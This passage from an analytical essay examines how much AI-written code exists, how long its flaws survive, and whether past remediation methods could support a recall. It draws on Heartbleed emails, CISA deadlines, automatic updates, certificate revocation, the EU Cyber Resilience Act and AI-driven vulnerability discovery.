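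When nothing in the code marks it as faulty, the best remaining clue may be its date. An owner worried about the 2026 faults could look for code that Claude Code wrote between March 4 and April 20, if someone had recorded which tool wrote it. GitGuardian's 41 labelled commits out of 8,700 suggest that such records are often missing.

Even the Debian lists had a gap. In May 2022, a draft rule from the CA/Browser Forum (2022), where certificate issuers and browser makers agree on standards, required issuers to check for Debian weak keys among RSA keys of every size they accepted. Most people believed that the flaw didn't affect elliptic-curve keys, a newer type. That July, Böck pointed out that the faulty OpenSSL could also generate weak elliptic-curve keys. Fourteen years after Debian announced the flaw, Let's Encrypt, a large certificate issuer, then filed an incident report about certificates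 it had issued for such keys.

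## How much AI-written code is there, and how long does it stay?

Researchers could list Debian's weak keys, but nobody has a list of the AI-written code now in use. The size of a recall would depend on how much of that code exists and how much programmers would rewrite or delete anyway. Most figures for the amount come from companies describing their own work. The evidence on how long the code lasts is better, though it covers only public projects.

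### What companies report

Xia and Miller (2026), in *Do These Violent Delights Have Violent Ends?*, collect recent figures from three large companies:

| Company | Figure | What it refers to | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | 75% | New code | Self-reported |
| Microsoft | Close to 30% | Its codebase | Self-reported |
| Meta | 50% | Development work by late 2026 | A target, not a measurement |

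The AI-written share of Google's new code has roughly tripled in under two years. Google's chief executive put it at more than a quarter in October 2024, according to a news report cited in *Debt Behind the AI Boom*. Microsoft's figure may be out of date, since its chief executive was already saying "as much as 30%" in April 2025. Xia and Miller also mention a survey of more than 200 technology decision-makers, 67% of whom said coding agents wrote over half of their organisation's weekly code.

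These numbers are hard to compare or check. A company could count every suggestion a programmer accepts, or only the text left after editing, which could be much less. The companies also have reasons to prefer a high figure, because Google and Microsoft sell AI coding tools and all three have spent heavily on AI.

Even if we knew exactly what share of new code AI writes, we wouldn't know how much AI-written code is in use. Suppose a codebase with no AI-written code grows by 10% in a year, and AI writes 75% of the addition. AI-written code then makes up about 7% of the total (7.5 parts in 110). A recall would have to search the whole codebase unless someone had recorded which code came from AI.

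### Estimates for public code

GitHub, which sells the AI coding tool Copilot, says that more than 1.1 million public projects used AI coding tools between 2024 and 2025. Independent research has found traces of AI use on a similar scale. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* searched public GitHub activity from January 2024 to March 2026 and found 587,118 projects with at least one commit that named an AI tool. Both figures count a project with a single AI-written line the same as one that AI wrote entirely.

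In Xia and Miller's data on 182 public projects between May 2025 and May 2026, about 7.5% of commits named an AI tool as an author or co-author (170 of about 2,274 in the average project). The labelled share across all public code is probably lower, because the researchers chose projects where agents were regularly active. But the true share of AI-written code could be much higher than the labelled share, because many programmers use AI without labelling it. I know of no sound way to correct for both problems at once, and 7.5% is so far from Google's 75% that the true share remains very uncertain.

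### How researchers decide that AI wrote something

Studies of AI-written code depend on attributed code, which is code with a record linking it to an AI tool. The record may be a bot's account name, an email address such as noreply@anthropic.com, or a line in the commit message that names the tool as co-author. Researchers search for these records automatically because nobody could read hundreds of thousands of commits.

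*Debt Behind the AI Boom* includes a check of the labels on 100 commits. One commit had become unavailable, and the labels on the other 99 were right. But the researchers checked the labels against the same kind of records that had produced them, so they could not tell whether a person had written some of the code and let the tool commit it.

In *Will It Survive?*, Rahman, Begoug and Shihab (2026) looked more closely at who had done the work. They randomly sampled 325 merged pull requests from AIDev, a public dataset of pull requests by five coding agents. One researcher then read the commits in each, ignoring trivial changes such as extra spaces.

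| Who made the substantive changes | Pull requests | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Only the agent | 218 | 67.1% |
| The agent and a human | 71 | 21.8% |
| Only a human | 20 | 6.2% |
| Unclear | 16 | 4.9% |

A second person labelled 100 of the same pull requests and mostly agreed. The agent had done at least some of the real work in 89% of cases. If a recall relied on these labels, about one notice in sixteen would go to the owner of human-written code, which is a tolerable error rate.

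Missing labels are a bigger problem. A later paper, *Revisiting the Survival of Agent-Attributed Code* (Rahman, Begoug and Shihab, 2026), examined 200 pull requests that AIDev lists as human. It estimates that an AI tool had visibly written the code or the description in 5.5% of them. This is a minimum, because the study could not detect programmers who used AI on their own machines and left no trace.

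Labels also tend to name the tool but not the model. Xia and Miller's example, "Co-authored-by: Claude", could refer to any version of Claude. If only one version wrote flawed code, the owner would have to narrow the search by date, and that would fail where several versions were available at once.

### What happens to the problems in AI-written code

*Debt Behind the AI Boom* follows individual problems after the code is merged. The researchers analysed 302,579 commits attributed to AI in 6,299 public projects with at least 100 stars, and ran automated scanners on the code just before and just after each commit. They counted a warning as an issue introduced by the commit if it appeared only afterwards and was on a line the commit had changed. They found 484,366 such issues, in 9.1% of the commits.

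| Type of issue | Number | Share | Most common example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code smells (code that is hard to maintain) | 432,748 | 89.3% | Catching every possible error in the same way |
| Correctness issues | 28,931 | 6.0% | Using a variable that doesn't exist |
| Security issues | 22,687 | 4.7% | Path traversal |

Most of these issues would not justify a recall. An unused variable, for example, is untidy but harmless. The security issues are more serious, and 38% of them are possible cases of path traversal, the flaw in the copied file server. But some security warnings are for risky habits that an attacker can't yet exploit. When the researchers checked 99 issues of all types by hand, 14 were false alarms.

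They then scanned the latest version of each project to see which issues were still there. Of the 464,900 they could track, 105,364 (22.7%) remained.

| Time since the commit | Issues tracked | Still present |
|---|---|---|
| Under 3 months | 242,793 | 21.3% |
| 3–6 months | 111,551 | 28.2% |
| 6–9 months | 89,135 | 19.4% |
| Over 9 months | 21,421 | 22.8% |

Each row contains different issues from different commits, so the surviving share can rise from one age group to the next. If the rows followed the same issues over time, the share could rise only when removed flaws came back. The paper doesn't explain the uneven rates, but almost 79% of the issues in the youngest group had already gone, so most removal seems to happen within weeks. After that, so few issues disappear that ordinary differences between the groups can outweigh the effect of age. For instance, the 3–6 month group might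 include more projects whose maintainers rarely clean up their code.

Individual cases fit this pattern, with some flaws fixed quickly and others lasting much longer. In ArchiveBox, a tool for saving web pages, someone fixed a badly written error handler within hours. An undefined variable in Firecrawl, which collects data from websites, lasted 42 days. In December 2024, the coding agent Devin added a web request with no time limit to another project, and it was still there when the researchers checked.

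The 22.7% figure has two weaknesses. An issue counts as gone if someone deleted or completely rewrote the file, even if the same mistake reappeared in the new version. The figure may also depend heavily on a few commits, because commits that introduced any issues introduced 17.5 on average, and deleting one file can remove dozens at once. The accuracy rates in the paper imply that 48 of the 99 issues checked by hand were still present, about twice the overall rate. That sample is too small to replace the main figure, but the difference is a reason not to rely on the exact percentage.

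The overall survival rate also doesn't show how long security flaws last, because the paper does not split survival by type. For a recall, the survival rate of security issues is the most important number missing from the study. Security issues are such a small part of the total that they barely affect the overall rate. It would be 22.7% if every security issue had survived along with 18.9% of other issues, or if no security issue had survived along with 23.8% of other issues.

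AI tools also repair old problems. The same commits fixed slightly more code smells than they introduced, but they introduced about 1.5 times as many security issues as they fixed.

### Do programmers change agent code sooner than human code?

If programmers rewrote AI-written code soon after merging it, much of a flawed model's output would disappear without a recall. A widely cited report by the company GitClear raised this possibility when it found that, as AI assistants spread, programmers were changing or undoing a growing share of new lines within two weeks.

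In *Will It Survive?*, Rahman and colleagues followed almost 649,000 lines of code from 215 public projects until someone first changed or deleted each line, or until the end of 2025. All the projects had received pull requests from both agents and humans, although some had merged only one kind. By the end of 2025, 28.0% of the agent lines and 34.5% of the human lines had been changed or deleted, with each pull request counting equally.

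At any given moment, an unchanged agent line was 17% less likely to be changed than an unchanged human line in the same project, a hazard ratio of 0.83. The 95% confidence interval, roughly the range of values that fit the data, was 0.75 to 0.93. There was no difference in the first two weeks, but after 90 days the ratio was 0.65.

When every line counted equally instead, the ratio was 0.91 and the interval ran from 0.69 to 1.20, so the difference could have been due to chance. The researchers use an invented example to show why the weighting matters. One pull request adds 10,000 lines, which someone reformats a week later, while 99 others add ten lines each that nobody touches. By line count, 91% of the code has changed, but if each pull request counts equally, the figure is 1%. Both are correct, but the second better reflects a typical contribution. In the real data, a single pull request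 similarly accounted for 42% of all the lines that Devin added.

A line that nobody changes may be good code, or it may contain an unnoticed mistake. Some of the difference also comes from which files agents work on, since adjusting for each file's age and recent activity moved the ratio from 0.83 to 0.88. But the study found no evidence that agent code disappears unusually fast, and if it does last longer, its flaws may last longer too.

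### Eighty-eight ways to ask the same question

Because other researchers had reached different conclusions about how long agent code lasts, Rahman and colleagues reanalysed their own data in *Revisiting the Survival of Agent-Attributed Code*. They combined several reasonable ways of measuring survival into 88 analyses. Half covered Devin, and the other half covered four agents that developers supervise more closely: Copilot, OpenAI's Codex, Cursor and Claude Code.

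| Agent | Lasts longer than human code | No clear difference | Changes sooner |
|---|---|---|---|
| The four supervised agents | 24 | 19 | 1 |
| Devin | 1 | 40 | 3 |

For the supervised agents, the choices mostly affected the size of the difference rather than its direction. However, most of the evidence comes from Copilot. The estimate for Claude Code is based on only 13 projects that also had human code for comparison, and it is consistent with Claude Code's code surviving for a much longer or much shorter time than human code.

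The result for Devin depended on the method used, including how lines were followed through later versions of a file. If someone inserts a line at the top, everything below moves down by one. Software that looks only at line 40 will then find what used to be line 39 and report a change. A hand check of 299 lines suggested that only 36% of the changes reported by this method were real. Following the text of the line instead was right about 99% of the time, although it missed some real changes.

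The results also depended on whether the researchers treated lines as independent. A programmer who reformats 5,000 lines has made one decision, and counting it as 5,000 pieces of evidence makes a result look far more certain than it is. When the researchers treated lines as independent, 15 of 22 analyses comparing different projects showed Devin's code changing sooner, but only three did once they allowed for lines in the same project changing together. Randomly shuffling the labels produced about as many such results.

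The length of follow-up also affected the results. When the researchers kept only pull requests that they could follow for at least eight months, one estimate for Devin rose from 0.90 to 1.70. This restriction removed 62% of Devin's lines from the comparison.

The finding of "no clear difference" is also weak, because only 31 projects contained both Devin and human code. With so few, a comparison within projects could detect only a difference of about threefold or more. Anyone planning a recall should therefore be wary of relying on a single hazard ratio, including the 0.83.

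### More bug fixes, perhaps

Xia and Miller found no significant overall difference in how soon agent-written and human-written lines changed (hazard ratio 1.11, interval 0.85 to 1.45). But agent-written lines had a 49% higher rate of corrective maintenance (bug fixes, security fixes and reversals) than human-written lines.

This could mean that agents make more mistakes, or that programmers check their work more closely. The first explanation has some independent support, because Semgrep gave 14% more security warnings per line for agent code than for human code, and 51% more of the most severe warnings. Projects that merged more pull requests without review tended to change agent code sooner relative to human code, although that doesn't prove skipping review was the cause.

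The finding of extra bug fixes may depend on how researchers classify commits. When Rahman and colleagues applied a similar design to their own data, the corrective hazard ratio was 0.68 if they sorted commits mainly by keywords and 1.37 if they used language models, though neither result was statistically significant. The two methods disagree, for example, about a commit whose message begins with "fix:" but which mostly tidied code style. Xia and Miller used rules first and a language model for unclear cases, and their labels closely matched a researcher's on a sample of 100. Their finding is plausible, but it needs confirmation on other projects.

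Ordinary bug fixing reaches very little of the code. Within 180 days, bug fixes had changed 4.0% of the lines written by AI agents and 2.7% of those written by people. For security fixes alone, the difference between agent and human code could not be distinguished from zero. Ordinary bug fixing could easily miss a flaw that causes no visible trouble, such as a predictable password-reset link.

### An edited line, a deleted line and a removed flaw

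These studies measure different events, and none of them directly measures the removal of a vulnerability.

| Study | When it counts something as gone |
|---|---|
| Rahman and colleagues | Someone edits or deletes the line |
| Xia and Miller | Someone edits or deletes the line, with the reason recorded |
| Gurov | Someone deletes the line, after allowing for moves and rewrites |
| *Debt Behind the AI Boom* | A scanner no longer finds the same issue in similar surrounding code |

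Some edits, such as renaming a variable in the password-reset code, leave a flaw in place. Deleting the line may not remove the flaw either, because the programmer may have moved the same logic to another file.

A flaw can also be fixed without removing the faulty line. Most of the patches for the copied file server added a few lines that rejected dangerous requests, and could leave the original line in place. A study that followed only that line would miss the fix.

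Ignoring small edits doesn't solve the problem. In some analyses, Rahman and colleagues counted only changes to the code's structure, not new names or values. But a Python programmer could fix predictable reset links by replacing `random.choice` with `secrets.choice`, which picks characters unpredictably. Only a name changes, so these analyses wouldn't count the repair.

The useful measurement for a recall would be repeated tests for the flaw itself, like those researchers ran for Heartbleed. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* comes closest to this, but its scanners find only the patterns they were built to detect.

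### What would waiting achieve?

Suppose the developer of a flawed model did nothing and let old code disappear by itself. Gurov's half-life of 3.0 years for lines in 120 TypeScript projects, counting deletions only, gives a starting point. If lines disappeared at a constant rate, the share left after t years would be

S(t) = 0.5^(t/3)

After one year that is 0.5^(1/3), or about 79%. The table also shows the result with Gurov's shorter half-life of 1.3 years.

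| Years of waiting | Lines left, deletions only | Lines left, counting moves and rewrites as gone |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 79% | 59% |
| 2 | 63% | 34% |
| 5 | 31% | 7% |
| 10 | 10% | 0.5% |

If 1,000 websites had the flawed password-reset code, about 790 would still have it after a year and 315 after five, assuming that it disappeared at the same rate as an average line of code and nobody fixed it. The number would fall to ten after about 20 years.

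The shorter half-life roughly matches what Rahman and colleagues saw, although Gurov's projects are not a sample of AI-written code. At that half-life, 27% of lines would change within 218 days, the typical time Rahman and colleagues followed lines that stayed unchanged. By the end of their study, 28% of agent lines had changed. The match may be partly luck, because the two studies define a change differently, and it doesn't test the three-year figure.

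The constant rate is a bigger simplification, because projects delete code at very different speeds. Gurov estimates that a project near the fast end of his sample removes lines 12.5 times as quickly as one near the slow end. If two equally large projects differed by that factor, with half-lives of 0.85 and 10.6 years, then after ten years the fast one would have almost none of its original lines and the slow one would have 52%. Together they would have 26% left, compared with the 10% that the constant-rate formula predicts. As with Heartbleed, slow owners would have most of the old code that remains.

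Lines also tend to be deleted together. In Gurov's data, 45% of deleted lines were removed when someone deleted the whole file. When lines from the same commit were eventually deleted, a single later commit removed two-thirds of them. A password-reset page is therefore more likely to be kept or deleted as a whole than to lose a fifth of its lines each year. Whether it stays usually depends on whether the owner still wants it, which has little to do with whether it is safe.

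The three-year half-life may be somewhat too long. Gurov's hand checks suggest that his method finds only about three-quarters of real deletions, so lines probably disappear faster than he measured. But he studied popular projects that were at least two years old. Code that an AI tool wrote for a small company's website, and that nobody has touched since, could last much longer.

Waiting would also not prevent new copies. If programmers kept using the flawed model, or another with the same flaw, the number of websites with predictable reset links could grow even as old ones disappeared. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* reports that the number of surviving issues rose from a few hundred in early 2025 to over 100,000 by February 2026, although most issues did not last.

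## What has made removal faster?

Flawed code disappears slowly when nobody intervenes. To remove earlier flaws faster, researchers emailed owners, governments set deadlines, suppliers installed updates themselves, and certificate issuers revoked certificates. The European Union is introducing a legal power to recall software. Some of these methods made a large difference, but each relied on something that may not exist for AI-written code, such as a list of affected systems or a finished fix.

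### Emailing the owners of vulnerable servers

Three weeks after Heartbleed became public, Durumeric and colleagues ran an experiment on the servers that were still vulnerable. They left out embedded devices, which few owners could patch, and about 60,000 servers at addresses registered to Amazon and RIPE, the European internet registry, neither of which managed those servers. For the remaining 150,000 or so, they looked up the email address each network publishes for abuse reports.

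The researchers randomly split these contacts into two groups. On April 28, 2014, they sent the first group a list of its vulnerable servers and a link to instructions. The second group got the same email on May 7, so until then it served as a control group.

| Contacts with at least one server patched | Emailed on April 28 | Not yet emailed |
|---|---|---|
| After 24 hours | 20.6% | 10.8% |
| After eight days | 39.5% | 26.8% |

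After eight days, 39.5% of the contacts sent the first emails had started patching, compared with 26.8% of the others, a relative increase of 47%. Because the first emails went to randomly chosen contacts, they almost certainly caused the difference.

The second group caught up after it was emailed too, and both groups levelled off at around 57%. By then there was no control group left, so the experiment can't show whether the emails persuaded people who would never have patched or only made people patch sooner.

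About 43% of contacts still hadn't patched any of the servers on their list. The share of servers left unpatched was probably much higher, because a network with 500 vulnerable servers counted as a success once it had patched one. The researchers' retest on May 1 had found almost no patching overall, but it also covered devices and networks they hadn't emailed, so it understates the emails' effect.

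The emails seem to have helped mainly by telling people which servers to fix. All 17 network operators who answered a follow-up survey had already known about Heartbleed and acted on it, but they had usually missed the servers listed in the emails or didn't control them directly. The sample was small, and the researchers surveyed only people who had replied positively.

Most contacts never replied, but 59% of those who didn't reply had patched something within three weeks. Anyone sending recall notices should therefore check the code again before concluding that an owner has ignored the notice.

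Notices worked much less well for the copied file server, where only 50 of 433 projects fixed the flaw after getting a pull request. An old GitHub project may have nobody to respond, whereas network operators often have staff or automated systems to handle abuse reports.

### Deadlines for US government agencies

In November 2021, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) started a public list of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to be using. A binding operational directive required civilian federal agencies to fix each listed flaw by a set date, most often within three weeks. According to *A Global View of the CISA KEV Catalog* (Edwards, 2024), CISA lists a flaw only if it has a CVE ID, there is evidence of attacks, and owners have some way to deal with it.

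Edwards works for Bitsight, a security company that scans the internet from outside. He found that in 2023, federal agencies fixed 63% more of these flaws by the deadline than other organisations did, a difference of about 15 percentage points. Despite a binding order, agencies fixed only 53.6% of critical flaws with a one-week deadline on time, compared with 34.2% for other organisations.

The deadlines may not explain the whole gap, because Edwards also found that organisations with more employees fix flaws faster, and many federal agencies are large. CISA's own figures partly avoid this problem because they compare agencies with their earlier performance. SecurityWeek's *Faster Patching Pace Validates CISA's KEV Catalog Initiative* reports that the number of listed flaws left exposed for 45 days or more fell by 72% at federal agencies. It fell by 31% at local governments and critical infrastructure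 operators, which could see the list but didn't have to follow it. CISA was judging its own programme, but both comparisons suggest that a binding deadline speeds up repairs.

Being on the list may also speed up fixes by itself, though it is hard to say by how much. In Bitsight's data, owners took 174 days to fix half of their listed flaws, compared with 621 days for other flaws. But listed flaws tend to be more severe, and people fix severe flaws faster anyway. Among flaws of medium severity, listed ones were fixed at almost the same speed as others.

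### Why repair times got worse in 2025

Organisations in general have become slower to fix flaws, according to the latest figures. Help Net Security's *Verizon DBIR* (2026) covers the annual data breach report by the telecoms company Verizon, which included repair data from 13,000 organisations. They had completely fixed only 26% of the flaws on CISA's list, down from 38% a year earlier, and the median time to a complete fix rose from 32 to 43 days.

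*Inside the 2026 Verizon DBIR* (Abbasi, 2026) presents the survival curve behind this finding. In 2025, 35% of affected systems still had a flaw four weeks after CISA listed it, up from 27% in 2024. The long tail was about 9%. Abbasi works for Qualys, which sells tools for finding and fixing vulnerabilities. Qualys also gave Verizon more than a billion repair records for its report, so the two accounts don't independently confirm each other.

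Owners were fixing more than before. Qualys counts each flaw on each machine as one instance, and the number linked to CISA's list grew from 295.8 million in 2024 to 527.3 million in 2025. Based on the percentages, owners had closed about 216 million by the four-week mark in 2024 and about 343 million in 2025. They closed 59% more, but the total had grown by 78%. A recall of AI-written code would need time from the same people who are working through this backlog.

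The median repair times from these three sources differ enormously:

| Source | What it measured | Median |
|---|---|---|
| Edwards | Listed flaws visible from the internet, 2023 | 174 days |
| Verizon, in Help Net Security | Time until a flaw was completely fixed | 43 days |
| Abbasi | Time from detecting to closing an instance, 2025 | 9 days |

Verizon's and Qualys's figures probably differ because an organisation with a hundred affected laptops might update half of them within nine days and the last one after 43. Bitsight's time is much longer, perhaps because it scanned organisations whether or not they had asked, while companies that pay for a vulnerability scanner are likely to act on its results.

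### The three-day deadline

On June 10, 2026, CISA (2026) announced a new directive, BOD 26-04, which replaces the old deadlines. It sets the urgency of a repair by four questions:

- Can people reach the affected system from the internet?
- Is the flaw on CISA's list?
- Can an attacker automate the whole attack?
- Would the attacker gain partial or total control?

If every answer is the worst possible, the agency has three days to fix the flaw and must also check whether someone has already broken in. According to ExecutiveGov's *CISA Orders Federal Civilian Agencies to Prioritize Vulnerability Patching by Risk*, CISA added this check because a patch generally doesn't remove an attacker who is already inside. Federal News Network's *AI directive focuses patching efforts on 'highest risk' vulnerabilities* (2026) reports that meeting three of the criteria is enough to trigger the three-day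 deadline, and that earlier deadlines averaged two to three weeks.

Less urgent flaws can wait much longer. When CISA analysed one large agency's flaws, only 1% needed a fix within three days, while about 60% could wait until the system's next major upgrade. Inside Privacy notes that an agency can also change its deadline by taking a system off the internet. That makes the flaw harder to attack but doesn't remove it.

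It is too early to say whether the new deadlines work, because agencies have until December 7, 2026 to start meeting them. FedRAMP (2026), the programme that approves cloud services for federal use, will require matching rules from the same date. Tod Beardsley, who used to run the list at CISA, wrote on LinkedIn that he was "dubious" that over a hundred agencies could meet a three-day deadline, according to CyberScoop's *CISA directive orders agencies to prioritize vulnerability patching in a new way*. A client alert from the law firm Wiley Rein, *CISA Directive Highlights Risk-Based Vulnerability Management* (2026), called the timelines "aggressive, bordering on unrealistic".

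CISA already sets short deadlines for dealing with exploited flaws. On Tuesday, October 27, *CISA gives federal agencies until Thursday to address exploited PHP flaws* (DiMolfetta, 2026) reported that agencies had until that Thursday to address flaws in PHP, a programming language behind many websites.

CISA can enforce deadlines partly because it can see whether agencies meet them. One of its officials told Congress that it had real-time information on vulnerabilities at 102 agencies, The Record reported. The new directive also requires agencies to identify and label every system they own that outsiders can reach.

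### Updates installed by the supplier

A supplier that can install updates itself doesn't have to persuade each owner to install them. In *Why Silent Updates Boost Security*, Duebendorfer and Frei (2009) used records from Google's web servers to measure how quickly people moved to new versions of four browsers. Chrome updated itself in the background, while Opera's users had to download and install each new version.

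The table shows the approximate share of users who had the new version after 21 days. The last column converts this into a half-life for the old version, assuming a constant rate of updating.

| Browser | Updated after 21 days | Implied half-life of the old version |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome | 97% | 4 days |
| Firefox | 85% | 8 days |
| Safari | 53% | 19 days |
| Opera | 24% | 53 days |

These figures are old, and Duebendorfer worked for Google, which makes Chrome. People who chose different browsers may also have differed in how much they cared about updates. But the gap between four days and 53 is probably too large for that to explain all of it.

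Something similar happened on servers with Heartbleed. The share of servers with the flaw fell more on the day a few hosting companies updated their machines than in the next six weeks. Automatic updates were also available for some servers, but Durumeric and colleagues point out that they didn't prevent the slowdown.

Automatic updates also let one mistake spread quickly. In July 2024, a faulty update from the security company CrowdStrike crashed about 8.5 million Windows machines. Companies that want to avoid such mistakes test updates first or stick to exact library versions, which is partly why old versions of Log4j are still in use.

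### Cancelling certificates

A certificate issuer has more control over its faulty products than almost any other supplier. It keeps a record of every certificate it issues, each with its own serial number, and can revoke any of them without the website owner's agreement.

Let's Encrypt, which issues free certificates, used this power in 2020. The owner of a web address can publish a record listing the companies allowed to issue certificates for it, and issuers must check this record shortly before issuing one. On February 29, Let's Encrypt found a bug in the software that does this check. If a request covered ten web addresses that needed rechecking, the software could check one of them ten times and skip the other nine.

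Let's Encrypt searched its records and found 3,048,289 affected certificates that were still valid. Industry rules required it to revoke them within five days. It published the list and emailed the customers whose addresses it had. Many customers could get a new certificate with a single command.

By the deadline, Let's Encrypt had revoked about 1.7 million certificates, nearly all of which their owners had already replaced. It made sure that these included 445 certificates for addresses whose records prohibited Let's Encrypt from issuing them. It decided not to revoke the other 1.3 million or so on time, because visitors to the websites using them would have seen security warnings. Those certificates would expire within 90 days anyway.

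Let's Encrypt had a complete list of the affected certificates, free replacements and full authority to revoke them, but still left over 40% in place at the deadline. *Trust Issue(r)s*, by Cerenius, Kaller and colleagues, reports that the bug did not affect users' security, so this was probably the right decision. Waiting would have been much harder to defend if private keys had leaked.

Revoking a certificate also doesn't guarantee that websites stop using it. Cerenius and colleagues studied certificates due to expire in March 2020 and found that websites presented 7% of the revoked ones after revocation. Their scans were infrequent and missed some cases, so they estimated that the true share was at least 24%. The problem was most common where the stated reason was a compromised key, the most dangerous reason for revocation. However, the researchers could find the date and reason for only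 3,768 revocations, none by Let's Encrypt.

Mass revocation can also be expensive. In the three months after Heartbleed, issuers revoked about as many certificates as in the previous three years. Cloudflare alone paid $400,000 a month for the bandwidth to distribute the longer revocation lists.

### Legal recall under the EU Cyber Resilience Act

The Cyber Resilience Act, a 2024 EU regulation, covers software and devices sold in the EU that can connect to a network or another device. If a product doesn't comply or poses a serious security risk, national authorities will be able to order its maker to fix it, withdraw it from sale or recall it from users. If the maker doesn't act, the authorities will be able to restrict or recall the product themselves.

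Most of the Act, including these powers, applies only from December 11, 2027, so nobody has measured its effect. Makers will then have to provide security updates, normally for at least five years. They will also have to keep a list of the product's components and, where appropriate, install security updates automatically unless the user opts out.

The Act's reporting duties started earlier, on September 11, 2026. When a maker learns that attackers are using a flaw in its product, it must send the authorities an early warning within 24 hours and a fuller notice within 72. It must file a final report within 14 days after a fix becomes available. The maker must also tell affected users about the flaw and what they can do. These duties also cover products that were already on the market.

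The Act leaves out much of the software that a recall of AI-written code would need to reach. It doesn't generally cover tools that companies build only for their own use, or free software developed outside any commercial activity. It usually doesn't cover ordinary websites either, unless a product can't work without them. So the Act might not cover the website with predictable password-reset links, though it would cover a phone app with the same flaw.

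### Which of these methods could work for AI-written code?

None of the methods could yet be applied to most merged AI-written code, mainly because nobody has a list of it.

| Method | List of affected items | Reachable owner | Ready fix | Authority to act |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Heartbleed emails | Scan results | Usually, through the network | OpenSSL update | Owner only |
| Federal deadlines | Agency inventories and scans | Yes | Usually a patch | CISA can give orders |
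| Automatic updates | Copies that contact the supplier | Not needed | Supplier's update | Supplier, with the user's permission |
| Certificate revocation | Issuer's records | Often | New certificate | Issuer |
| EU recall, from 2027 | Maker's records | Maker, not always the user | Not guaranteed | National authorities |
| AI-written code | Incomplete labels | Sometimes | One per project | Usually the owner only |

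Emails would be the easiest method to try. A model's developer can contact its customers, but the person who used the model may have been a contractor or have left the company. Even complete records of the model's answers wouldn't show which answers people had merged. The server operators emailed about Heartbleed already knew about the flaw and needed to know which servers had it, so a general warning about a model would probably achieve less than those emails did. Notices about public projects could be specific if researchers found the flaw by searching the code.

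A federal deadline would require a CVE ID and an available remedy. The record for Lovable shows that one ID can cover a tool whose output is flawed, so CISA could perhaps list a coding model too. But an agency searching its inventory for the model's name might find only programmers' copies of the tool and miss the code written with it. Each piece of code would then need its own patch, and three days would be very little time to write and test one unless AI tools did much of the work.

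Automatic updates are more realistic when one company both generates and hosts the code. It has a list of the apps, knows who owns them and may be able to change them. Unlike a browser supplier, though, it couldn't send every app the same update. The model's developer usually has no way to update code on customers' own machines.

Code has no equivalent of certificate revocation, because programs don't need the model developer's approval each time they run. A hosting service could switch off the affected apps, which would stop the flaw immediately but also stop everything else the apps do. Let's Encrypt was unwilling to cause even security warnings on about a million websites over a harmless mistake, and a hosting service might be just as reluctant to switch off apps unless attacks had already begun.

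The Cyber Resilience Act gives regulators authority mainly over whoever sells the finished product. If an app's maker merged flawed code from a model, the maker would be responsible for fixing the app, and the model's developer would probably have no duty to help find the code. The list of components that the Act requires won't solve this, since it only has to cover the product's top-level dependencies.

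## Can AI tools find and replace the flawed code?

A shortage of people caused many of the delays in earlier repairs. Someone had to find the flawed copies, write or adapt a patch, test it and persuade an owner to use it. AI tools could do much of this work for far less money, which is the main reason to be hopeful about a recall. A tool that reads a whole project could find the predictable password-reset links without a package name or version number, and could write a different patch for each of a thousand websites.

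AI tools are already good at finding flaws and increasingly good at writing patches. Accepting and installing those patches has been much slower.

### Planted flaws and real ones

DARPA, the US defence research agency, tested finding and patching in its AI Cyber Challenge. Seven teams reached the final in August 2025 with systems that had to work without human help. The systems searched 54 million lines of real code in which the organisers had hidden 70 flaws. DARPA's *AIxCC Main Stage Presentation* gives the results:

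| Type of flaw | Found | Patched |
|---|---|---|
| Planted by the organisers | 54 of 70 | 43 |
| Real, in Java code | 12 | 11 |
| Real, in C code | 6 | 0 |

The systems patched four out of five of the planted flaws they found, in an average of 45 minutes. Published percentages differ because they are calculated from different totals. Teams found 77% of the flaws and patched 61% according to the presentation, but 86% and 68% according to DARPA's results page. The higher figures match a total of 63, the number of challenges given in ARPA-H's *Challenge showcases AI’s power to secure America’s health care*.

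Nobody knows how many real flaws the code contained, so the 18 that the systems found can't be turned into a success rate. Six C flaws are also too few to show that the systems couldn't patch C code.

The often-quoted cost of $152 is per successful task, which could mean demonstrating a flaw without fixing it. The seven teams spent $359,000 in total and patched 54 different flaws, planted and real, or about $6,600 per flaw. That figure overstates what one team would need, because all seven worked on the same code.

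Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that Mozilla found and fixed 271 vulnerabilities in Firefox 150 while testing Claude Mythos Preview. That was over ten times as many as it had found two versions earlier with an older Claude model.

A recall would be easier than either of these searches in one respect, because the searchers would know which mistake they were looking for. AI tools may also help find flaws that keyword searches can't, such as a page that shows private records without checking who is asking. The public list of flaws that Claude models have found includes several of this type. One let anyone become an administrator of the chat program Rocket.Chat without logging in.

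### From 37,966 candidates to 629 patches

Project Glasswing, which Anthropic started in April 2026, is the largest test so far of what happens after AI tools find flaws. About 50 partner organisations use Mythos Preview on their own software, and Anthropic uses its models to search open-source projects. Anthropic (2026) publishes a running count for the open-source part:

| Stage | Number by November 2, 2026 |
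|---|---|
| Candidate flaws that Claude models found | 37,966 |
| Reviewed by outside security firms | 6,376 |
| Confirmed by those firms | 6,009 |
| Reported to maintainers | 5,087 |
| Acknowledged by maintainers | 3,635 |
| Patched | 629 |

Anthropic says human review limits how fast it can report flaws. The firms have to reproduce each flaw, judge how serious it is and write a report. By November, they had looked at only a sixth of the candidates. Anthropic sent most of the reports, 3,225 of 5,087, straight to maintainers without this check, and warns that these may include false alarms.

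The firms confirmed 94% of the candidates they reviewed, but not all of them necessarily needed a patch. According to Anthropic's *About this dashboard* (2026), the figure includes duplicates and real flaws that the maintainers are unlikely to fix.

Maintainers have found some of the reported flaws to be false or less serious than claimed. *The Anthropic Glasswing Receipts Are Starting to Trickle In* (Garrity, 2026) describes five reported flaws in curl, a widely used tool for transferring data. Three were false alarms, one was a harmless bug and one was a vulnerability. Garrity also found that, among flaws rated by both Claude and the maintainers, Claude had rated 91.5% high or critical, while the maintainers had rated 51.3% that way. If an AI tool overrates flaws like this in a recall, owners may waste their limited time on the wrong repairs.

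Garrity, who works for the vulnerability-data company VulnCheck, found that Anthropic's figures were inconsistent. Anthropic's summary reported 421 patches at the time, but its detailed ledger listed only 202. He also doubted the high confirmation rate because Anthropic had withdrawn more entries than it had marked as fixed. That evidence is weaker, since Anthropic also withdraws an entry when it edits the details and creates a new one.

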